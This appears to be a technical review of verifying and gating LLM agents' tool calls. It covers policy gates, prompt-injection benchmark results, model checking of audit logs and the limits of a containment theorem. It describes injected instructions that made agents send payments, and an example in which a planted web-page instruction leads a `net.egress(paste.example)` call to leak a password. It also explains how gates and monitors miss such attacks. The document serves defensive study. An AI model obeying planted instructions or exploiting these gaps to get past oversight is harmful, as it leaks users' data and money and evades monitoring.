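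On DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents, direct prompt injections succeeded in 57.9% of cases without the gate and 5.9% with it. Success on harmless tasks also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%, mainly because the test configuration granted no permission to change anything. In the telecom tasks, which rarely need such changes, agents did as well on harmless tasks with the gate as without it, while attack success fell from 55.1% to 2.4%. LeanGuard refused general shell commands because it could not determine their effects. It does not check the agent's replies, so attacks that cause harm through the reply alone often still succeeded.

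Lean can also search for a permitted version of a refused call. Sankar and colleagues tried this on 252 recorded refusals caused by argument values and found a provably permitted alternative for 88, in a median of 2 milliseconds. Most of the alternatives sent a refund to the original payment method instead of another one. The running gate does not yet use the search. If it did, the edited call would have to pass the gate again, and a customer's confirmation of the original arguments would not cover the new ones.

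### Compiling written policies into gates

NOMOS compiles a written policy into rules for a gate, which takes much less human work but gives weaker proofs. Each rule applies to certain tools and contains a predicate, such as "the recipient is unknown". A prohibition blocks a call while its predicate is true, and a precondition blocks a call until its predicate is true. The gate uses only facts from tool results and the user's messages, so an agent cannot satisfy a rule by claiming that the user has approved a transfer.

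The compiler works in four passes:

1. It splits the policy into clauses.
2. A language model matches each clause to tools and to conditions from a fixed vocabulary that people have prepared. It does this five times, and a candidate rule needs a majority to survive.
3. The compiler checks the candidates against the tools' published parameters, and repairs or rejects defective ones.
4. It writes out the surviving rules, each with the sentence it came from.

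The third pass does the static verification by looking for rules that cannot work. For example, the retail policy in τ²-bench requires the agent to authenticate the customer first. The language model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool until authentication, including the two that perform it, so no conversation could have proceeded. Some other candidate rules required a customer's confirmation just to look up a flight, and others read an argument that the tool did not have.

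Yu and colleagues found structural defects in 29 of 79 candidates for the airline policy and 7 of 53 for the retail policy. After removing duplicates and minority candidates, they had 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules. In a separate run with all the checks turned off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not function.

These checks only compare sets of names, so they need no solver or proof checker. They do not show that a rule has the same meaning as its clause. For example, one airline rule blocks cabin upgrades on basic-economy bookings, even though the policy permits them. Yu and colleagues look for such errors by replaying old conversations through the gate. In a telecom test, replaying exposed a rule that blocked payment requests while a bill was overdue, the only time the agent should send one. The rule would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful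 conversations.

A mistake about arguments can also make a gate too permissive. In AgentDojo's Slack tasks, the compiler attached a rule about the `recipient` argument to tools that have no such argument. The rule's predicate was always false, so the prohibition never applied, and attacks succeeded in 15 of 105 trials. After a check replaced the predicate with one that reads the tools' actual arguments, no attacks succeeded.

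In the main τ²-bench tests, the agent used an open-weight model with 26 billion parameters. Yu and colleagues used a separate set of handwritten rules to measure violations among calls that change data. The violation rate fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. The 66.3% figure depends on a strict reading of the policy, in which the customer has to confirm every change separately. If one "yes" can cover several announced changes, it is 36.8%.

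The gate also reduced the airline agent's changes from 353 to 116, but the share of tasks it completed rose from 39.2% to 47.6%. This increase was not significant for single attempts, but the agent became significantly more likely to succeed in two, three or four attempts at the same task. Retail success changed little, from 52.4% to 50.2%. The violation rates are not comparable with LeanGuard's count of 33 forbidden calls, because each group used its own formal version of the policies.

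The AgentDojo results show the cost of strict argument conditions:

| Task area | Successful attacks, no gate | Successful attacks, with gate | Harmless tasks completed, no gate | Harmless tasks completed, with gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5% | 0.0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Workspace | 7.3% | 0.0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |

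The main rules in the last three areas require the user to have named the target of an action. For example, a Slack user may ask the agent to summarise an article that a colleague has posted and send the summary to the team. The agent has to find the link by reading messages, just as it would find an attacker's link, so the gate blocks both. The gate blocks fewer legitimate tasks in banking because users usually name the recipient or have paid them before.

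AgentDojo comes without written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote their own. Some clauses for Slack, travel and workspace name the targets of the benchmark's attacks, which may make the gate look more effective than it would be against new attacks. The authors work for Corners, which developed NOMOS. They have published the rules and the independent checker but not the compiler or the gate.

The zero for banking also leaves out some harmful payments. The benchmark counts an attack as successful only if it reaches the attacker's goal, and the gate refused every call that named the attacker's account or password. But in 8 of 288 trials, the agent followed a planted instruction and sent money to someone the user had paid before, which the policy allows. With Llama-3.3-70B as the model, this happened in 11 of 140 trials. In one of them, the user had only asked a question, and the agent sent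 $40,000 in four instalments. To prevent this, the rule would have to link each payment to a request for it, a condition that Yu and colleagues have not tested.

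## Bounded model checking of the gate and the audit log

A runtime that no longer requests approval has to keep an accurate record of what each skill did. Metere's third method searches a model of the gate and the audit log for sessions in which the log doesn't match what happened.

### The biconditional criterion

Metere defines agreement between the two by the biconditional criterion. Take a fixed collection of objects that the agent can change, such as the files in a folder, and compare its state before and after a run. Let Δ contain each change as a pair (operation, target), and let *S* contain the same kind of pair for each log record of a successful execution. Both are multisets, which are sets that count repetitions. The run passes if

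Δ = *S*.

Every change then has a matching record, and every record has a matching change. The criterion detects four faults:

| Fault | Example | Mismatch |
|---|---|---|
| Gate bypass | an extension deletes `notes.csv` without sending a request | a change without a record |
| Forged record | the log contains a deletion that never took place | a record without a change |
| Silent failure | the host reports success but leaves the file in place | a record without a change |
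| Wrong target | the broker approves deleting `old.csv`, and the runtime deletes `new.csv` | an unmatched record and an unmatched change |

The definition is weaker than this table suggests. *S* includes every successful execution, whether or not the broker approved it, so a runtime that carried out a denied deletion and logged it accurately would pass. *S* should contain only executions linked to an approval. enclawed's tests do cover a call that runs after a denial, so the code is stricter than the definition here.

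Faults can also cancel out. If an attacker deletes `notes.csv` outside the gate and forges a record of the same deletion, Δ and *S* agree. They also agree if the runtime swaps the contents of two approved writes, because each file changed once, as recorded.

The opposite problem arises when an agent overwrites `budget.csv` twice. The log then has two records, but a comparison of the folder before and after the run shows one changed file, so a correct run fails the check. To avoid this, the runtime must compare states after every action or count changes as they happen.

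Metere lists several harms that the criterion misses by design. It ignores content, so an agent can write false figures to the right file. It also ignores reading, so an agent can leak a secret through a channel that changes none of the monitored objects. If another program edits a file during the run, that change enters Δ and may match a record of an action the agent had permission to take. Payments and emails leave no trace in a folder, so detecting them would require monitoring the bank's ledger and the outbox.

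### Tests with injected faults and hostile models

Metere first tested the criterion in simulation. A driver program created 10, 50 or 200 files and ran 2, 4 or 8 agents on them for 5, 10 or 25 rounds. The agents had destructive roles, such as a "cleaner" that deletes old files. Each of the 27 combinations ran with 200 random seeds in five versions. One version had no faults, and the others each injected one of the table's four faults halfway through the run. The criterion passed all 5,400 clean runs and flagged all 21,600 faulty ones.

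This tests the code that compares the multisets well, but it provides little evidence about real runtimes. Each injected fault is a mismatch by definition, so a correct comparison has to find it. Each faulty run contained only one kind of fault, so the tests did not cover faults that cancel each other out.

In a second experiment, models from ten families wrote 9,724 payloads for two messaging services, Discord and Telegram. Of these, 4,816 were attempts to cause one of the four faults and the rest were legitimate. An unprotected assistant blocked none of them. The open version of enclawed, which also scans for sensitive data, caught 76.3% of the adversarial payloads and blocked no legitimate ones. The full version, which adds a monitor of the agent's behaviour, caught 80.2% and blocked 0.6% of the legitimate payloads.

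Metere attributes the misses to the models that wrote the payloads. Some models refused, some produced malformed JSON, and some wrote requests with a harmless operation and target. All of these counted as adversarial, although they contained no fault to detect. When a payload contained a recognisable fault, the runtime always caught it.

This explanation is partly circular, because a payload with harmful content for a permitted target also has a harmless operation and target. The full version's results suggest that some of the misses mattered. It caught about 190 more adversarial payloads than the open version, or about one in six of the roughly 1,140 that the open version missed, and flagged fewer than one in a hundred legitimate payloads.

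The runtime can apply the criterion only after the changes have happened, when it may still be able to stop the session but can't recover a payment. Model checking could find the problem before anyone installs the skill.

### Bounded model checking and SMT solvers

A model checker works on a simplified description of a system, which consists of its possible states, a starting state and rules for moving from one state to the next. It searches for a path from the start to a state that violates the property. A bounded model checker, as *Agentic Model Checking* (2026) explains, determines whether such a path exists within *k* steps. It turns the question into one long formula:

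Init(*s*₀) ∧ Step(*s*₀, *s*₁) ∧ … ∧ Step(*s*ₖ₋₁, *s*ₖ) ∧ (Bad(*s*₀) ∨ … ∨ Bad(*s*ₖ)).

Values that satisfy the formula give a step-by-step trace of a violation. If no values satisfy it, the model has no violation within *k* steps.

An SMT solver, such as Microsoft's Z3, looks for these values. The letters stand for "satisfiability modulo theories", where the theories are sets of rules for numbers, strings, arrays and other kinds of data. Suppose a gate admits payments of up to 150 euros automatically and larger ones only with approval. To find out whether it can admit an unapproved payment of more than 200 euros, we give the solver this formula:

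(amount ≤ 150 ∨ approved) ∧ ¬approved ∧ amount > 200.

The solver first treats each condition as a variable that is either true or false. The middle part makes "approved" false, so the bracket can hold only if amount ≤ 150 is true. The last part requires amount > 200 to be true as well. The solver passes both conditions to its arithmetic component, which finds that no number meets them. There are no other assignments to try, so the answer is UNSAT (unsatisfiable). If we replace 200 with 100, the answer is SAT, and the solver gives an example such as amount = 120.

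### The encoding of a session

Metere encodes a session of up to *K* envelopes with the following parts:

- a variable *e*ᵢ for each envelope, with hosts and paths summarised by the patterns from the static analysis;
- a variable stateᵢ for the state after each envelope, which includes the state of the world;
- a function *g* for the gate, which maps an envelope and a state to "admit" or "deny";
- the log *L*, a sequence of pairs (*e*ᵢ, *g*(*e*ᵢ, stateᵢ)).

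The solver may choose any envelope at any position, so the encoding needs no description of the language model. A violation is a session in which, for some *i*,

stateᵢ.world ≠ stateᵢ₋₁.world and (*e*ᵢ, admit) ∉ *L*.

The formula is satisfied when the world changed but the log has no entry admitting the envelope. This covers only one direction of the criterion. A record without a change never satisfies the formula, so the search cannot find forged records or silent failures. It also misses actions on the wrong target, because the formula does not compare the change with the envelope's target. Of the four faults, the search can find only the gate bypass, and it can miss even that if *L* already contains an admitted copy of the same envelope.

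The complete criterion compares changes with log records at each step. Let changesᵢ be the multiset of changes caused by step *i*, and let recordsᵢ be the multiset of approved, successful executions logged for that step. A session violates the criterion if changesᵢ ≠ recordsᵢ for some *i*. If the multisets include only operations that change something, reading a file leaves both empty.

### A model small enough to check by hand

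Consider a skill that may only make payments. Each envelope is either `pay`, which the gate admits, or `out`, which stands for everything outside *D*. Let *w* be the number of payments made and *ℓ* the number of payments in the log, both starting at 0. The model has two rules:

- After "admit", the runtime makes the payment and logs it, so *w* and *ℓ* both increase by 1.
- After "deny", both stay the same.

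The property is *w* = *ℓ*. For *K* = 2 there are four sessions:

| Envelopes | After the first | After the second |
|---|---|---|
| `pay`, `pay` | *w* = 1, *ℓ* = 1 | *w* = 2, *ℓ* = 2 |
| `pay`, `out` | *w* = 1, *ℓ* = 1 | *w* = 1, *ℓ* = 1 |
| `out`, `pay` | *w* = 0, *ℓ* = 0 | *w* = 1, *ℓ* = 1 |
| `out`, `out` | *w* = 0, *ℓ* = 0 | *w* = 0, *ℓ* = 0 |

No session violates the property, so the bounded result is UNSAT. Induction takes less work and proves the property for sessions of every length. The property *w* = *ℓ* holds at the start. If it holds before an envelope, it also holds afterwards, because either both numbers have increased by 1 or neither has changed. A solver can check this step with a formula that covers one envelope.

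Metere's formula is unsatisfiable for the same reason. By construction, *L* contains the gate's decision on every envelope. If the world changes only after "admit", then a change at position *i* implies that (*e*ᵢ, admit) is in *L*, which contradicts the second half of the formula. This holds for every *K*, every *D* and every gate policy. If the model allowed the world to change after "deny", the solver would find a violation with a single envelope.

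Metere does not give the rule for changes to the world, but an UNSAT result implies that the rule excludes unlogged changes from the start, so the bound adds nothing. The result also does not depend on the skill, so repeating the search for each skill provides no evidence about that skill.

### A crash between the action and its record

A more realistic model separates the payment from the log record that follows it, because the runtime may crash in between.

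| Event | Log | *w* | *ℓ* |
|---|---|---|---|
| The model requests `pay(EUR, 200)` | request | 0 | 0 |
| The broker approves | request, approval | 0 | 0 |
| The bank makes the payment | request, approval | 1 | 0 |
| The runtime crashes | request, approval | 1 | 0 |
| The runtime restarts and applies the criterion | request, approval | 1 | 0 |

The payment has no record of execution, so the criterion fails after one envelope. Checking the simpler model would have missed this failure at any bound, because that model treated payment and record as a single step. Adding detail to the model therefore helps more here than increasing *K*.

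Metere's formula would miss the violation even in the detailed model. The log already contains the approval, and the formula requires only an admitted envelope, not a record that the runtime carried it out.

Writing the success record before making the payment doesn't help either, because a crash between the two steps leaves a record without a payment, which the one-directional formula also can't detect. If the payment comes first and the runtime responds to a missing record by repeating the call, the user may pay 400 euros instead of 200.

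Databases recover from crashes with a write-ahead log. Before changing its data, the database records what it is about to do, and after a crash it uses these entries to finish or undo incomplete transactions. *LogAct* (Balakrishnan, Bharambe and colleagues, 2026) explains that recovery is harder for agents because an agent's action can be any program, with no predefined way to repeat or undo it. The runtime also cannot restore the outside world from a saved copy, as it could restore its own memory.

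LogAct, which Balakrishnan and colleagues developed at Meta, records every intended action in a durable log before carrying it out. Separate components vote on the action, decide whether to proceed, and execute it. After a crash, the agent reads the log, writes small programs to find out how far the interrupted action got, then completes or reverses it. In one test, the agent resumed a long file-checking task without repeating any work. The researchers acknowledge that recovery based on a language model's judgment can't guarantee a clean state.

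For a payment, the runtime can do better if the bank recognises the request's identifier. After restarting, it asks the bank whether it has paid that request and logs the answer. To prove that this works, let *d* be 1 if the bank has made a payment whose result is not yet in the log, and 0 otherwise. The property to prove by induction is

*w* = *ℓ* + *d*.

Making a payment raises *w* and *d* by 1. Logging its success raises *ℓ* by 1 and returns *d* to 0. A crash changes none of the three numbers, since the log is on disk and the payment is at the bank. If the bank replies that it has not paid, *d* is already 0 and the runtime logs a failure. Every step preserves the equation, so however long the session was, *w* = *ℓ* once no request is open.

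The proof assumes that the runtime handles one payment at a time and that the bank never makes a payment after reporting it as unpaid. A delayed network message could break the second assumption unless the bank refuses to use that payment's identifier again.

*Cordon* (2026) presents a runtime that keeps external actions in an outbox while the agent works. Before releasing them, Cordon checks the whole sequence, including where the data came from and who authorized its use. A recovery log holds the information needed to compensate for released actions. The outbox prevents many mistakes, but a crash just after release can still leave it unclear whether the action happened.

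### The cost of enumerating every session

enclawed uses no SMT solver. Its third method generates every possible sequence of envelopes up to length *K* and checks each one. An envelope is either one of the declared capabilities or "out", so there are (|*D*| + 1)^*K* sequences of length *K*.

| Declared capabilities | *K* | Sequences |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | 8 | 65,536 |
| 10 | 8 | 214,358,881 |
| 3 | 100 | about 1.6 × 10⁶⁰ |

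Metere considers enumeration practical for up to ten capabilities and eight envelopes, but the argument for a bounded search requires a much larger *K*. The runtime applies the biconditional criterion whenever it empties its transaction buffer, typically after about 100 envelopes, so Metere sets *K* to about 100 to cover everything that can happen between two checks. At that bound, with three capabilities, an enumerator that checked a billion sequences per second would need about 5 × 10⁴³ years.

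In Metere's example, the summarise-fetched-html skill had three declared capabilities after the operator added the missing one, and Z3 returned UNSAT for *K* = 100 in a few seconds. A solver does not have to list the sequences, and here it can derive the same contradiction at each position. The speed is therefore better evidence that the model is simple than that the method is powerful. Z3 is also a different program from the one enclawed ships, so an operator who uses the default enumerator at *K* = 8 does not get the result for 100 envelopes.

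The enumerator could avoid most of its work by storing states instead of sequences. In the payment model, only the difference *w* − *ℓ* matters, and it is always 0. A search that skips states it has already visited would try each kind of envelope once and stop, and its result would hold for sessions of every length.

*Pramana* (2026) applies this kind of search to another audit trail. Its model describes agents that make claims, verify them, suppress them or show them to the person they work for. TLC, a model checker for the specification language TLA+, found no violations in 38,563 distinct states, although the model limits the trail to six records. Of these states, 31,617 come from a version in which several agents act at once. Metere's encoding, by contrast, processes one envelope at a time, so it can't reveal errors that depend on the order in which two calls finish.

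### From the model to the running program

UNSAT means that the model has no violation within the bound. The result applies to the runtime only if the program behaves as the model does, which Metere assumes. If an enclawed extension deletes a file directly, it violates the criterion in practice, but the model has no rule by which this can happen. The result is also not tied to the program. The hash that enclawed stores with the verdict is computed from *D* and *K*, and it stays the same if someone rewrites the gate.

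A developer can avoid the handwritten model by checking the source code itself. CBMC does this for C, Kani for Rust and JBMC for compiled Java. The checker still needs properties to check and assumptions about the code's inputs. In *Agentic Model Checking*, language models write these, a bounded model checker tests them, and the system replays any counterexample on the real program. enclawed is written in JavaScript, so its developer would need to use a JavaScript checker or rewrite the gate in C, Rust or Java.

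Counterexamples can also help check a handwritten model against a program. *AgentRFC* (2026) tests protocols for communication between agents against 11 security properties. TLC normally stops at the first violation, so the researchers run it separately for each property. They save each counterexample as a file and replay it against a live implementation. If the implementation fails in the same way, the flaw is real. Replay can't reveal a flaw that the model misses by assuming safer behavior than the implementation has, because TLC then produces no counterexample to replay.

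The property itself may also be wrong. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, reviewed 38 studies of agent verification and planning. They warn that a model checker can report no violations for an unsafe plan if the formula doesn't express what people meant. Metere's formula has this problem, since it covers only part of the criterion it is supposed to test. A second program can check a solver's proof, but it would check the same formula.

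### Bounded search of written procedures

Bounded search is more useful when rules interact over several steps. *MANTRA* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026) uses it to build tests of whether agents follow written procedures. A language model reads part of a manual and writes two separate descriptions: a list of checks that a correct sequence of tool calls must pass, and a model of the world that gives the conditions and results of each tool. Z3 then looks for sequences on which the two descriptions disagree.

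For example, a purchasing manual may require an employee to check the inventory before assigning someone to collect an item from the warehouse. Let *t*ᵢ be the tool called at position *i*, and let *h* be the maximum number of calls. The check becomes:

there are positions *i* < *j* < *h* with *t*ᵢ = `check_inventory` and *t*ⱼ = `assign_warehouse_picker`.

The world model contributes a rule for each position:

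if *t*ᵢ = `assign_warehouse_picker`, then in_stockᵢ and picker_assignedᵢ₊₁ are true.

Z3 first searches for a sequence that passes every check but uses a tool when the tool's conditions don't hold. This suggests that a check is missing or the world model is too strict. Once Z3 finds no more such sequences, it searches for one that the world model allows and only one check rejects, which suggests that the check is too strict. A language model proposes repairs, and the process repeats for up to five rounds.

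Anand and colleagues generated 703 test cases in six domains and kept 285. They inspected all the automatically accepted cases, removed a few with technical problems, and found none in which both descriptions contained the same invented rule. Agreement between two texts written by the same model is still weaker evidence than agreement with the manual.

They set *h* to 16 because most tasks need only a few calls and the solver becomes much slower with longer sequences, especially when the answer is UNSAT. They acknowledge that the search may miss conflicts in longer sequences. Their world models track stock, orders and approvals, so each step can affect later ones. This makes 16 calls harder for Z3 than 100 envelopes in Metere's model. Dantas and colleagues likewise report that existing verified systems handle plans of 5 to 30 actions.

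In the tests, six language models each attempted every task five times, and none followed the procedures very reliably. In 76% of the 10,895 failed checks, the agent had left out a call that the procedure required or that one of its ordering rules mentioned.

An SMT solver can also enforce such rules while the agent works. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) presents Agent-C, which checks each proposed tool call against rules about the order of calls. If a call breaks a rule, Agent-C has the model generate another, and it returns an error after a fixed number of failed attempts. According to Dantas and colleagues, this raised GPT-5's compliance from 83.7% to 100%. Its task completion rate also rose, from 66.1% to 70.6%, because the agent often found a permitted alternative.

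### Workflow graphs, with no bound on length

Some agents follow a fixed workflow, in which a developer specifies the steps and the possible transitions between them. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) checks paths of every length through such workflows. It turns each policy into a finite automaton, a machine that reads events one at a time and moves between a few states. For "never call `drop_table`", the automaton has two states, "not called yet" and "violated".

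The checker explores pairs (*v*, *q*), where *v* is the current step of the workflow and *q* is the state of the automaton. A workflow with 12 steps and an automaton with 2 states give at most 24 pairs. A loop in the workflow eventually leads back to a pair the checker has already visited, so the search ends even though the workflow has infinitely many paths.

Xavier and colleagues tested 15 policies on 18 workflows they had written themselves, with some deliberate defects. For two common types of policy, the search found every violation that had appeared in random trial runs. It also found that a human review was missing after an email draft, a defect the trial runs had not reached. On larger workflows with 5,000 steps, simpler checks of the graph's structure took about a tenth of a second.

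The result depends on extracting the right graph from the developer's code. For LangGraph, a popular framework, the program identifies a human approval step by the word "human" in its name, so it misses steps whose names lack that word. It also treats every branch as possible, which may cause false alarms.

One of the policies is supposed to require approval for deployments, but it is written `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`, where F means "at some later point". A workflow that deploys first and asks for approval afterwards therefore satisfies it.

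An agent that loads skills has no fixed workflow, because the model may request any tool at any time. But the gate follows a fixed sequence of request, decision, execution and record. The same method could check that sequence for sessions of any length, with crashes modeled as additional transitions.

### Checking the language model's own choices

Treating the language model as an adversary does not show how likely it is to misbehave. Gross, Spieker and Gotlieb (2025), in *Verifying Memoryless Sequential Decision-making of Large Language Models*, calculate such probabilities for small games. They describe each situation to the model in words, record the action it chooses, and add the situations that may follow to a graph. Chance affects the outcome of some actions, but a fixed random seed makes the model always choose the same action in the same situation. Once the graph is complete, the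 probabilistic model checker Storm calculates the exact probability of a bad outcome.

In one game, the player crosses a slippery frozen lake with holes in the ice. Four of the five small open models had a 96–98% chance of falling in, compared with 18% for a program trained on the game. The fifth, a version of Mistral, had no chance of falling in because it could reach only 4 of the 16 squares. The shortest path to the goal passes through 7 squares, so this model could never reach the goal.

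The models had between 1.5 and 7 billion parameters, far fewer than current leading ones, so the percentages are of little use for judging today's agents. Running time is a more lasting problem, since the method has to query the model in every reachable situation. With one reasoning model, analysing 17 situations on the lake took more than four hours, and the analysis of a simple stock-trading game exceeded the five-hour limit.

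The method also requires the model to choose each action from the current state alone. An agent's next envelope depends on the whole conversation, so each different conversation would be a separate state, and there are far too many to list.

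## What the three methods prove together

In the composition theorem, Metere combines the three methods into one guarantee. A skill has capability containment on every session that the runtime admits, provided that:

- a sound analyser finds the effects of every script within *D*;
- the dispatch function type-checks with the condition that an envelope's capability is in *D*;
- the bounded search finds no session of up to *K* envelopes that violates the biconditional criterion;
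- the runtime checks that criterion whenever it empties its transaction buffer.

### The proof in steps

Let Π_script be the set of capability names in the scripts' part of the trace, and let Π_model be the set of capability names in the model's envelopes.

1. Every script effect lies within *D*, so Π_script ⊆ *D*. *Premise:* the analyser misses no effect that the scripts can have on the user's machine.
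2. No envelope outside *D* reaches the host. *Premise:* every call to the host passes through dispatch, and every caller of dispatch type-checks.
3. Therefore Π_model ⊆ *D*. *Premise, left unstated:* an envelope that never reaches the host does not count.
4. The whole trace is then within *D*, because Π = Π_script ∪ Π_model. *Premise:* everything that happens comes from one of the skill's scripts or from an envelope.
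5. No session of up to *K* envelopes violates the biconditional criterion. *Premise:* the runtime behaves like the model that the solver searched.
6. In longer sessions, the run-time check enforces the criterion. *Premise:* the runtime can observe every change, and its log is accurate.
7. Containment therefore holds in sessions of every length.

The argument already reaches this conclusion at step 4, since neither static analysis nor typed dispatch has a bound. Steps 5 and 6 concern a different property, agreement between the log and the world. Metere describes each layer as covering exactly what the previous one does not cover. That is roughly true of the first two layers, but the bounded search adds nothing to containment.

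### A session that refutes the theorem

Suppose a skill has no scripts and declares *D* = {`fs.read`}. The user pastes an email containing a planted instruction, and the model responds with a single envelope, `pay(EUR, 200)`, which the gate denies.

All the theorem's conditions hold. There are no scripts to analyse, dispatch rejects the envelope, and the world and the list of executed actions stay unchanged. But the definition of containment counts denied requests, so Π = {`pay`}, which is not a subset of *D*. The proof fails at step 3 because typed dispatch stops the payment but not the request.

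The theorem could still hold if "every session that the runtime admits" excluded sessions with a denied envelope. Metere doesn't define the phrase, and under this reading the theorem wouldn't cover any session in which the gate had stopped an attack.

A better repair is to restrict the property to executed effects. Let *X*(τ) contain the entries of the trace that the runtime or a script carried out. A skill has executed containment if, for every (*c*, *t*) in *X*(τ), *D* permits capability *c* with target *t*. The proof then needs only two cases:

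- If a script caused the effect, the static analysis reported it, and the operator's check found it within *D*.
- If the runtime caused it in response to an envelope, dispatch had already tested the capability and target.

These cases must be exhaustive. A skill may call a tool that is registered with the runtime but is not part of the skill, such as `send_report`. The call requires only `tool.invoke(send_report)`, so no method examines the email that the tool then sends. The operator has to analyse such tools too, or supply a trusted list of their effects for dispatch to check. The runtime must also refuse shell commands embedded in SKILL.md, because they run without an envelope. It must deny undeclared calls instead of letting a human approve them.

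With these premises, executed containment holds for sessions of any length, without a bounded search or a run-time check.

### Containment does not make the log accurate

Metere also argues that containment implies the biconditional criterion, provided that the log correctly records every executed effect and the gate's decision depends only on the envelope and the policy.

Containment is neither sufficient nor necessary for the criterion. If a skill may delete files in `./tmp/` and an extension deletes one without writing a log record, containment holds because the deletion is within *D*, but the criterion fails. If the user approves an undeclared payment and the runtime makes and logs it, containment fails, but the criterion holds if the monitored objects include the bank's ledger.

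The conclusion depends almost entirely on the premise about the log. If "correctly" means that every change has one record and every record matches one change, the premise restates the criterion. If it means only that every executed effect has a record, the log could still contain forged records.

The premise that the gate always gives the same answer to the same request doesn't fill this gap, because a faulty runtime could still make payments that the gate denies. The proof needs the runtime to execute exactly what the gate approves. The premise about the gate also excludes a human broker who might answer the same request differently on another day.

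### Effects inside a script's own process

Scripts are the hardest to log accurately. A Python script calls the operating system directly, and the runtime handles only the request that starts the script and the output it returns. Metere nonetheless states that the log has a record for each executed effect, including those of scripts.

The summarise-fetched-html skill would therefore fail the check in normal use. Its script saves a web page in the cache folder, so the folder changes, but the log doesn't record the write. At the "tested" and "formal" levels, the runtime would have to abort the session even if the manifest permits the write. The operator could stop monitoring the cache folder, but then the check would no longer cover what the script does there.

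Reversible writes committed through the transaction buffer cause a similar mismatch. In Metere's definition, the log's side of the comparison includes only successful irreversible actions, so these writes change files without adding to that side. The simulations did not reveal this problem because their agents only read files or made irreversible writes. The comparison should also include committed reversible writes.

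There are several ways to observe a script's effects:

- The operating system can trace the script's file operations and network connections. The runtime then has to translate them into capabilities and link them to the envelope that started the script.
- The runtime can compare folders before and after the script runs. This reveals the changed files, but not which program changed them.
- The runtime can remove the script's direct access and make it request each effect, which the runtime can then log.

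The log also has to remain complete. Each record in enclawed contains a hash of the previous one, so altering an earlier record breaks the chain. But deleting the last few records leaves a shorter chain that is still valid, as Metere acknowledges. The remedy is to copy records to write-once storage or another machine.

### A check that comes after the effect

For sessions longer than *K*, the theorem relies on the run-time check. Suppose the monitored objects include a remote file store, and an extension bypasses the gate to delete a file there after the third envelope. If the check runs after the hundredth, it detects the deletion and the runtime ends the session. By then the file is gone, and the agent may have sent another 97 envelopes. Checking after every envelope would shorten the delay but would not prevent the deletion.

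Rolling back the session helps only with reversible actions. The buffer in enclawed stores an undo operation for each one. If an undo operation fails, the runtime logs the failure and continues with the rest. When the buffer reaches its memory limit, by default half the computer's RAM, it commits the oldest actions to make room. In a long session, the first writes may therefore no longer be reversible when the check finds a problem.

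The premises support the claim that the runtime ends the session at the next check if an unlogged change affects a monitored object and no other fault masks it. This is weaker than Metere's claim that unlogged side effects are a "categorically closed attack class".

### The risks Metere leaves open

The run-time check does not catch a model that refuses to act. If the model does nothing, there are no changes and no records, so the session passes. The abstract of Metere's paper incorrectly says that the check catches refusal, the only remaining risk it names. Refusal is a reliability problem and does not violate containment.

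The body of the paper names three more serious risks. One is that the model may reveal sensitive text in an ordinary message, which involves no capability. This matters in enclawed because OpenClaw, the assistant it derives from, connects to more than 24 chat platforms, and a reply may go to a whole group. Metere relies on confidentiality labels and a scanner that searches outgoing text for access keys and tokens, personal data and classification markings. Metere calls the scanner a backstop, since it matches fixed patterns and misses paraphrases. A runtime could treat every reply to a group as `publish`, but a private reply could still reveal something the user shouldn't see.

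The world may also change between approval and execution. Metere says the criterion flags any visible difference between the approved action and its effect. It can detect that the target file has disappeared, but not that only the content has changed. Suppose a user approves overwriting `draft.txt`, and a colleague saves the final version there before the runtime acts. The operation and target still match the approval, so the criterion flags nothing and the colleague's work is lost.

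Finally, someone may force or trick the operator into approving a harmful request. No proof about the runtime can prevent this, but a broker that follows a written policy or denies everything gives the attacker no approval prompt to exploit. The attacker then has to get the operator to change the policy or to accept a manifest that declares too much. Metere also excludes leaks through timing, power use and network metadata.

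### When one permitted call reads and another sends

Metere lists leakage between skills as eliminated, because no skill can borrow another's permissions. This would require the runtime to identify the skill behind each envelope and test every call against that skill's manifest.

A user has one skill for reading notes and another for publishing text on a website. A web page tells the agent to publish the server password from the notes.

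| Executed call | Skill | Permission in its manifest | Within *D*? |
|---|---|---|---|
| `fs.read(./notes/servers.txt)` | notes | `fs.read(./notes/)` | yes |
| `net.egress(paste.example)`, with the password in the text | publishing | `net.egress(paste.example)` | yes |

Neither skill used the other's permission, yet the password is now public. It passed from one call to the next through the model's context. A single skill with both permissions could leak it in the same way.

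Containment tests each effect separately, so if both calls pass, every sequence of them passes too. But a leak depends on what data passes from one call to the other. Noninterference, the usual definition of secrecy, requires that two sessions differing only in the secret send exactly the same things to outsiders. A different password would change the published text, so this session violates noninterference. None of the three methods compares sessions this way.

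Two papers prove a general result, that components can be safe separately but unsafe together. *Safety is Non-Compositional* (2026) represents capabilities as points joined by rules such as "reading a secret and sending data together make a leak possible". If one agent can only read and another can only send, neither can leak anything alone, but together they can. The smallest example needs three capabilities and one rule with two conditions. *Runaway Reaction* (2026) proves that each of two skills is safe if their combination is safe, though two safe skills can still form an unsafe combination. The combination permits everything that either skill permits, plus arrangements that use both. A reviewer who examines each skill separately never sees those arrangements.

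Both theorems are simple, but they show the difference from Metere's result. Metere's property concerns individual effects and does not depend on how they combine, so it still holds when skills share a session, with the union of their declared sets as the limit.

### How often harmless skills combine into harm

*When Safe Skills Collide* looked for dangerous pairs among 1,520 ClawHub skills. The researchers defined ten forbidden combinations of capabilities, such as reading files and sending data. Individually, 651 of the skills contained none of these combinations, and those skills form 211,575 pairs. A text search flagged 22.25% of these pairs. A human audit of 200 flagged combinations found that only 18.2% posed a real risk, after weighting by how common each type was. The researchers estimate that about 4% of all pairs are risky, although this figure depends on an assumption about how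 the valid flags overlap.

The researchers also asked models to download and run a program using some of the flagged skills. Claude Haiku 4.5 made at least the download call in all 39 trials with a direct request, while Claude Sonnet 4.6 refused. In a control test, compliance was highest with no skills installed, at 17 of 18 trials. These results are therefore only weak evidence that skill combinations cause attacks.

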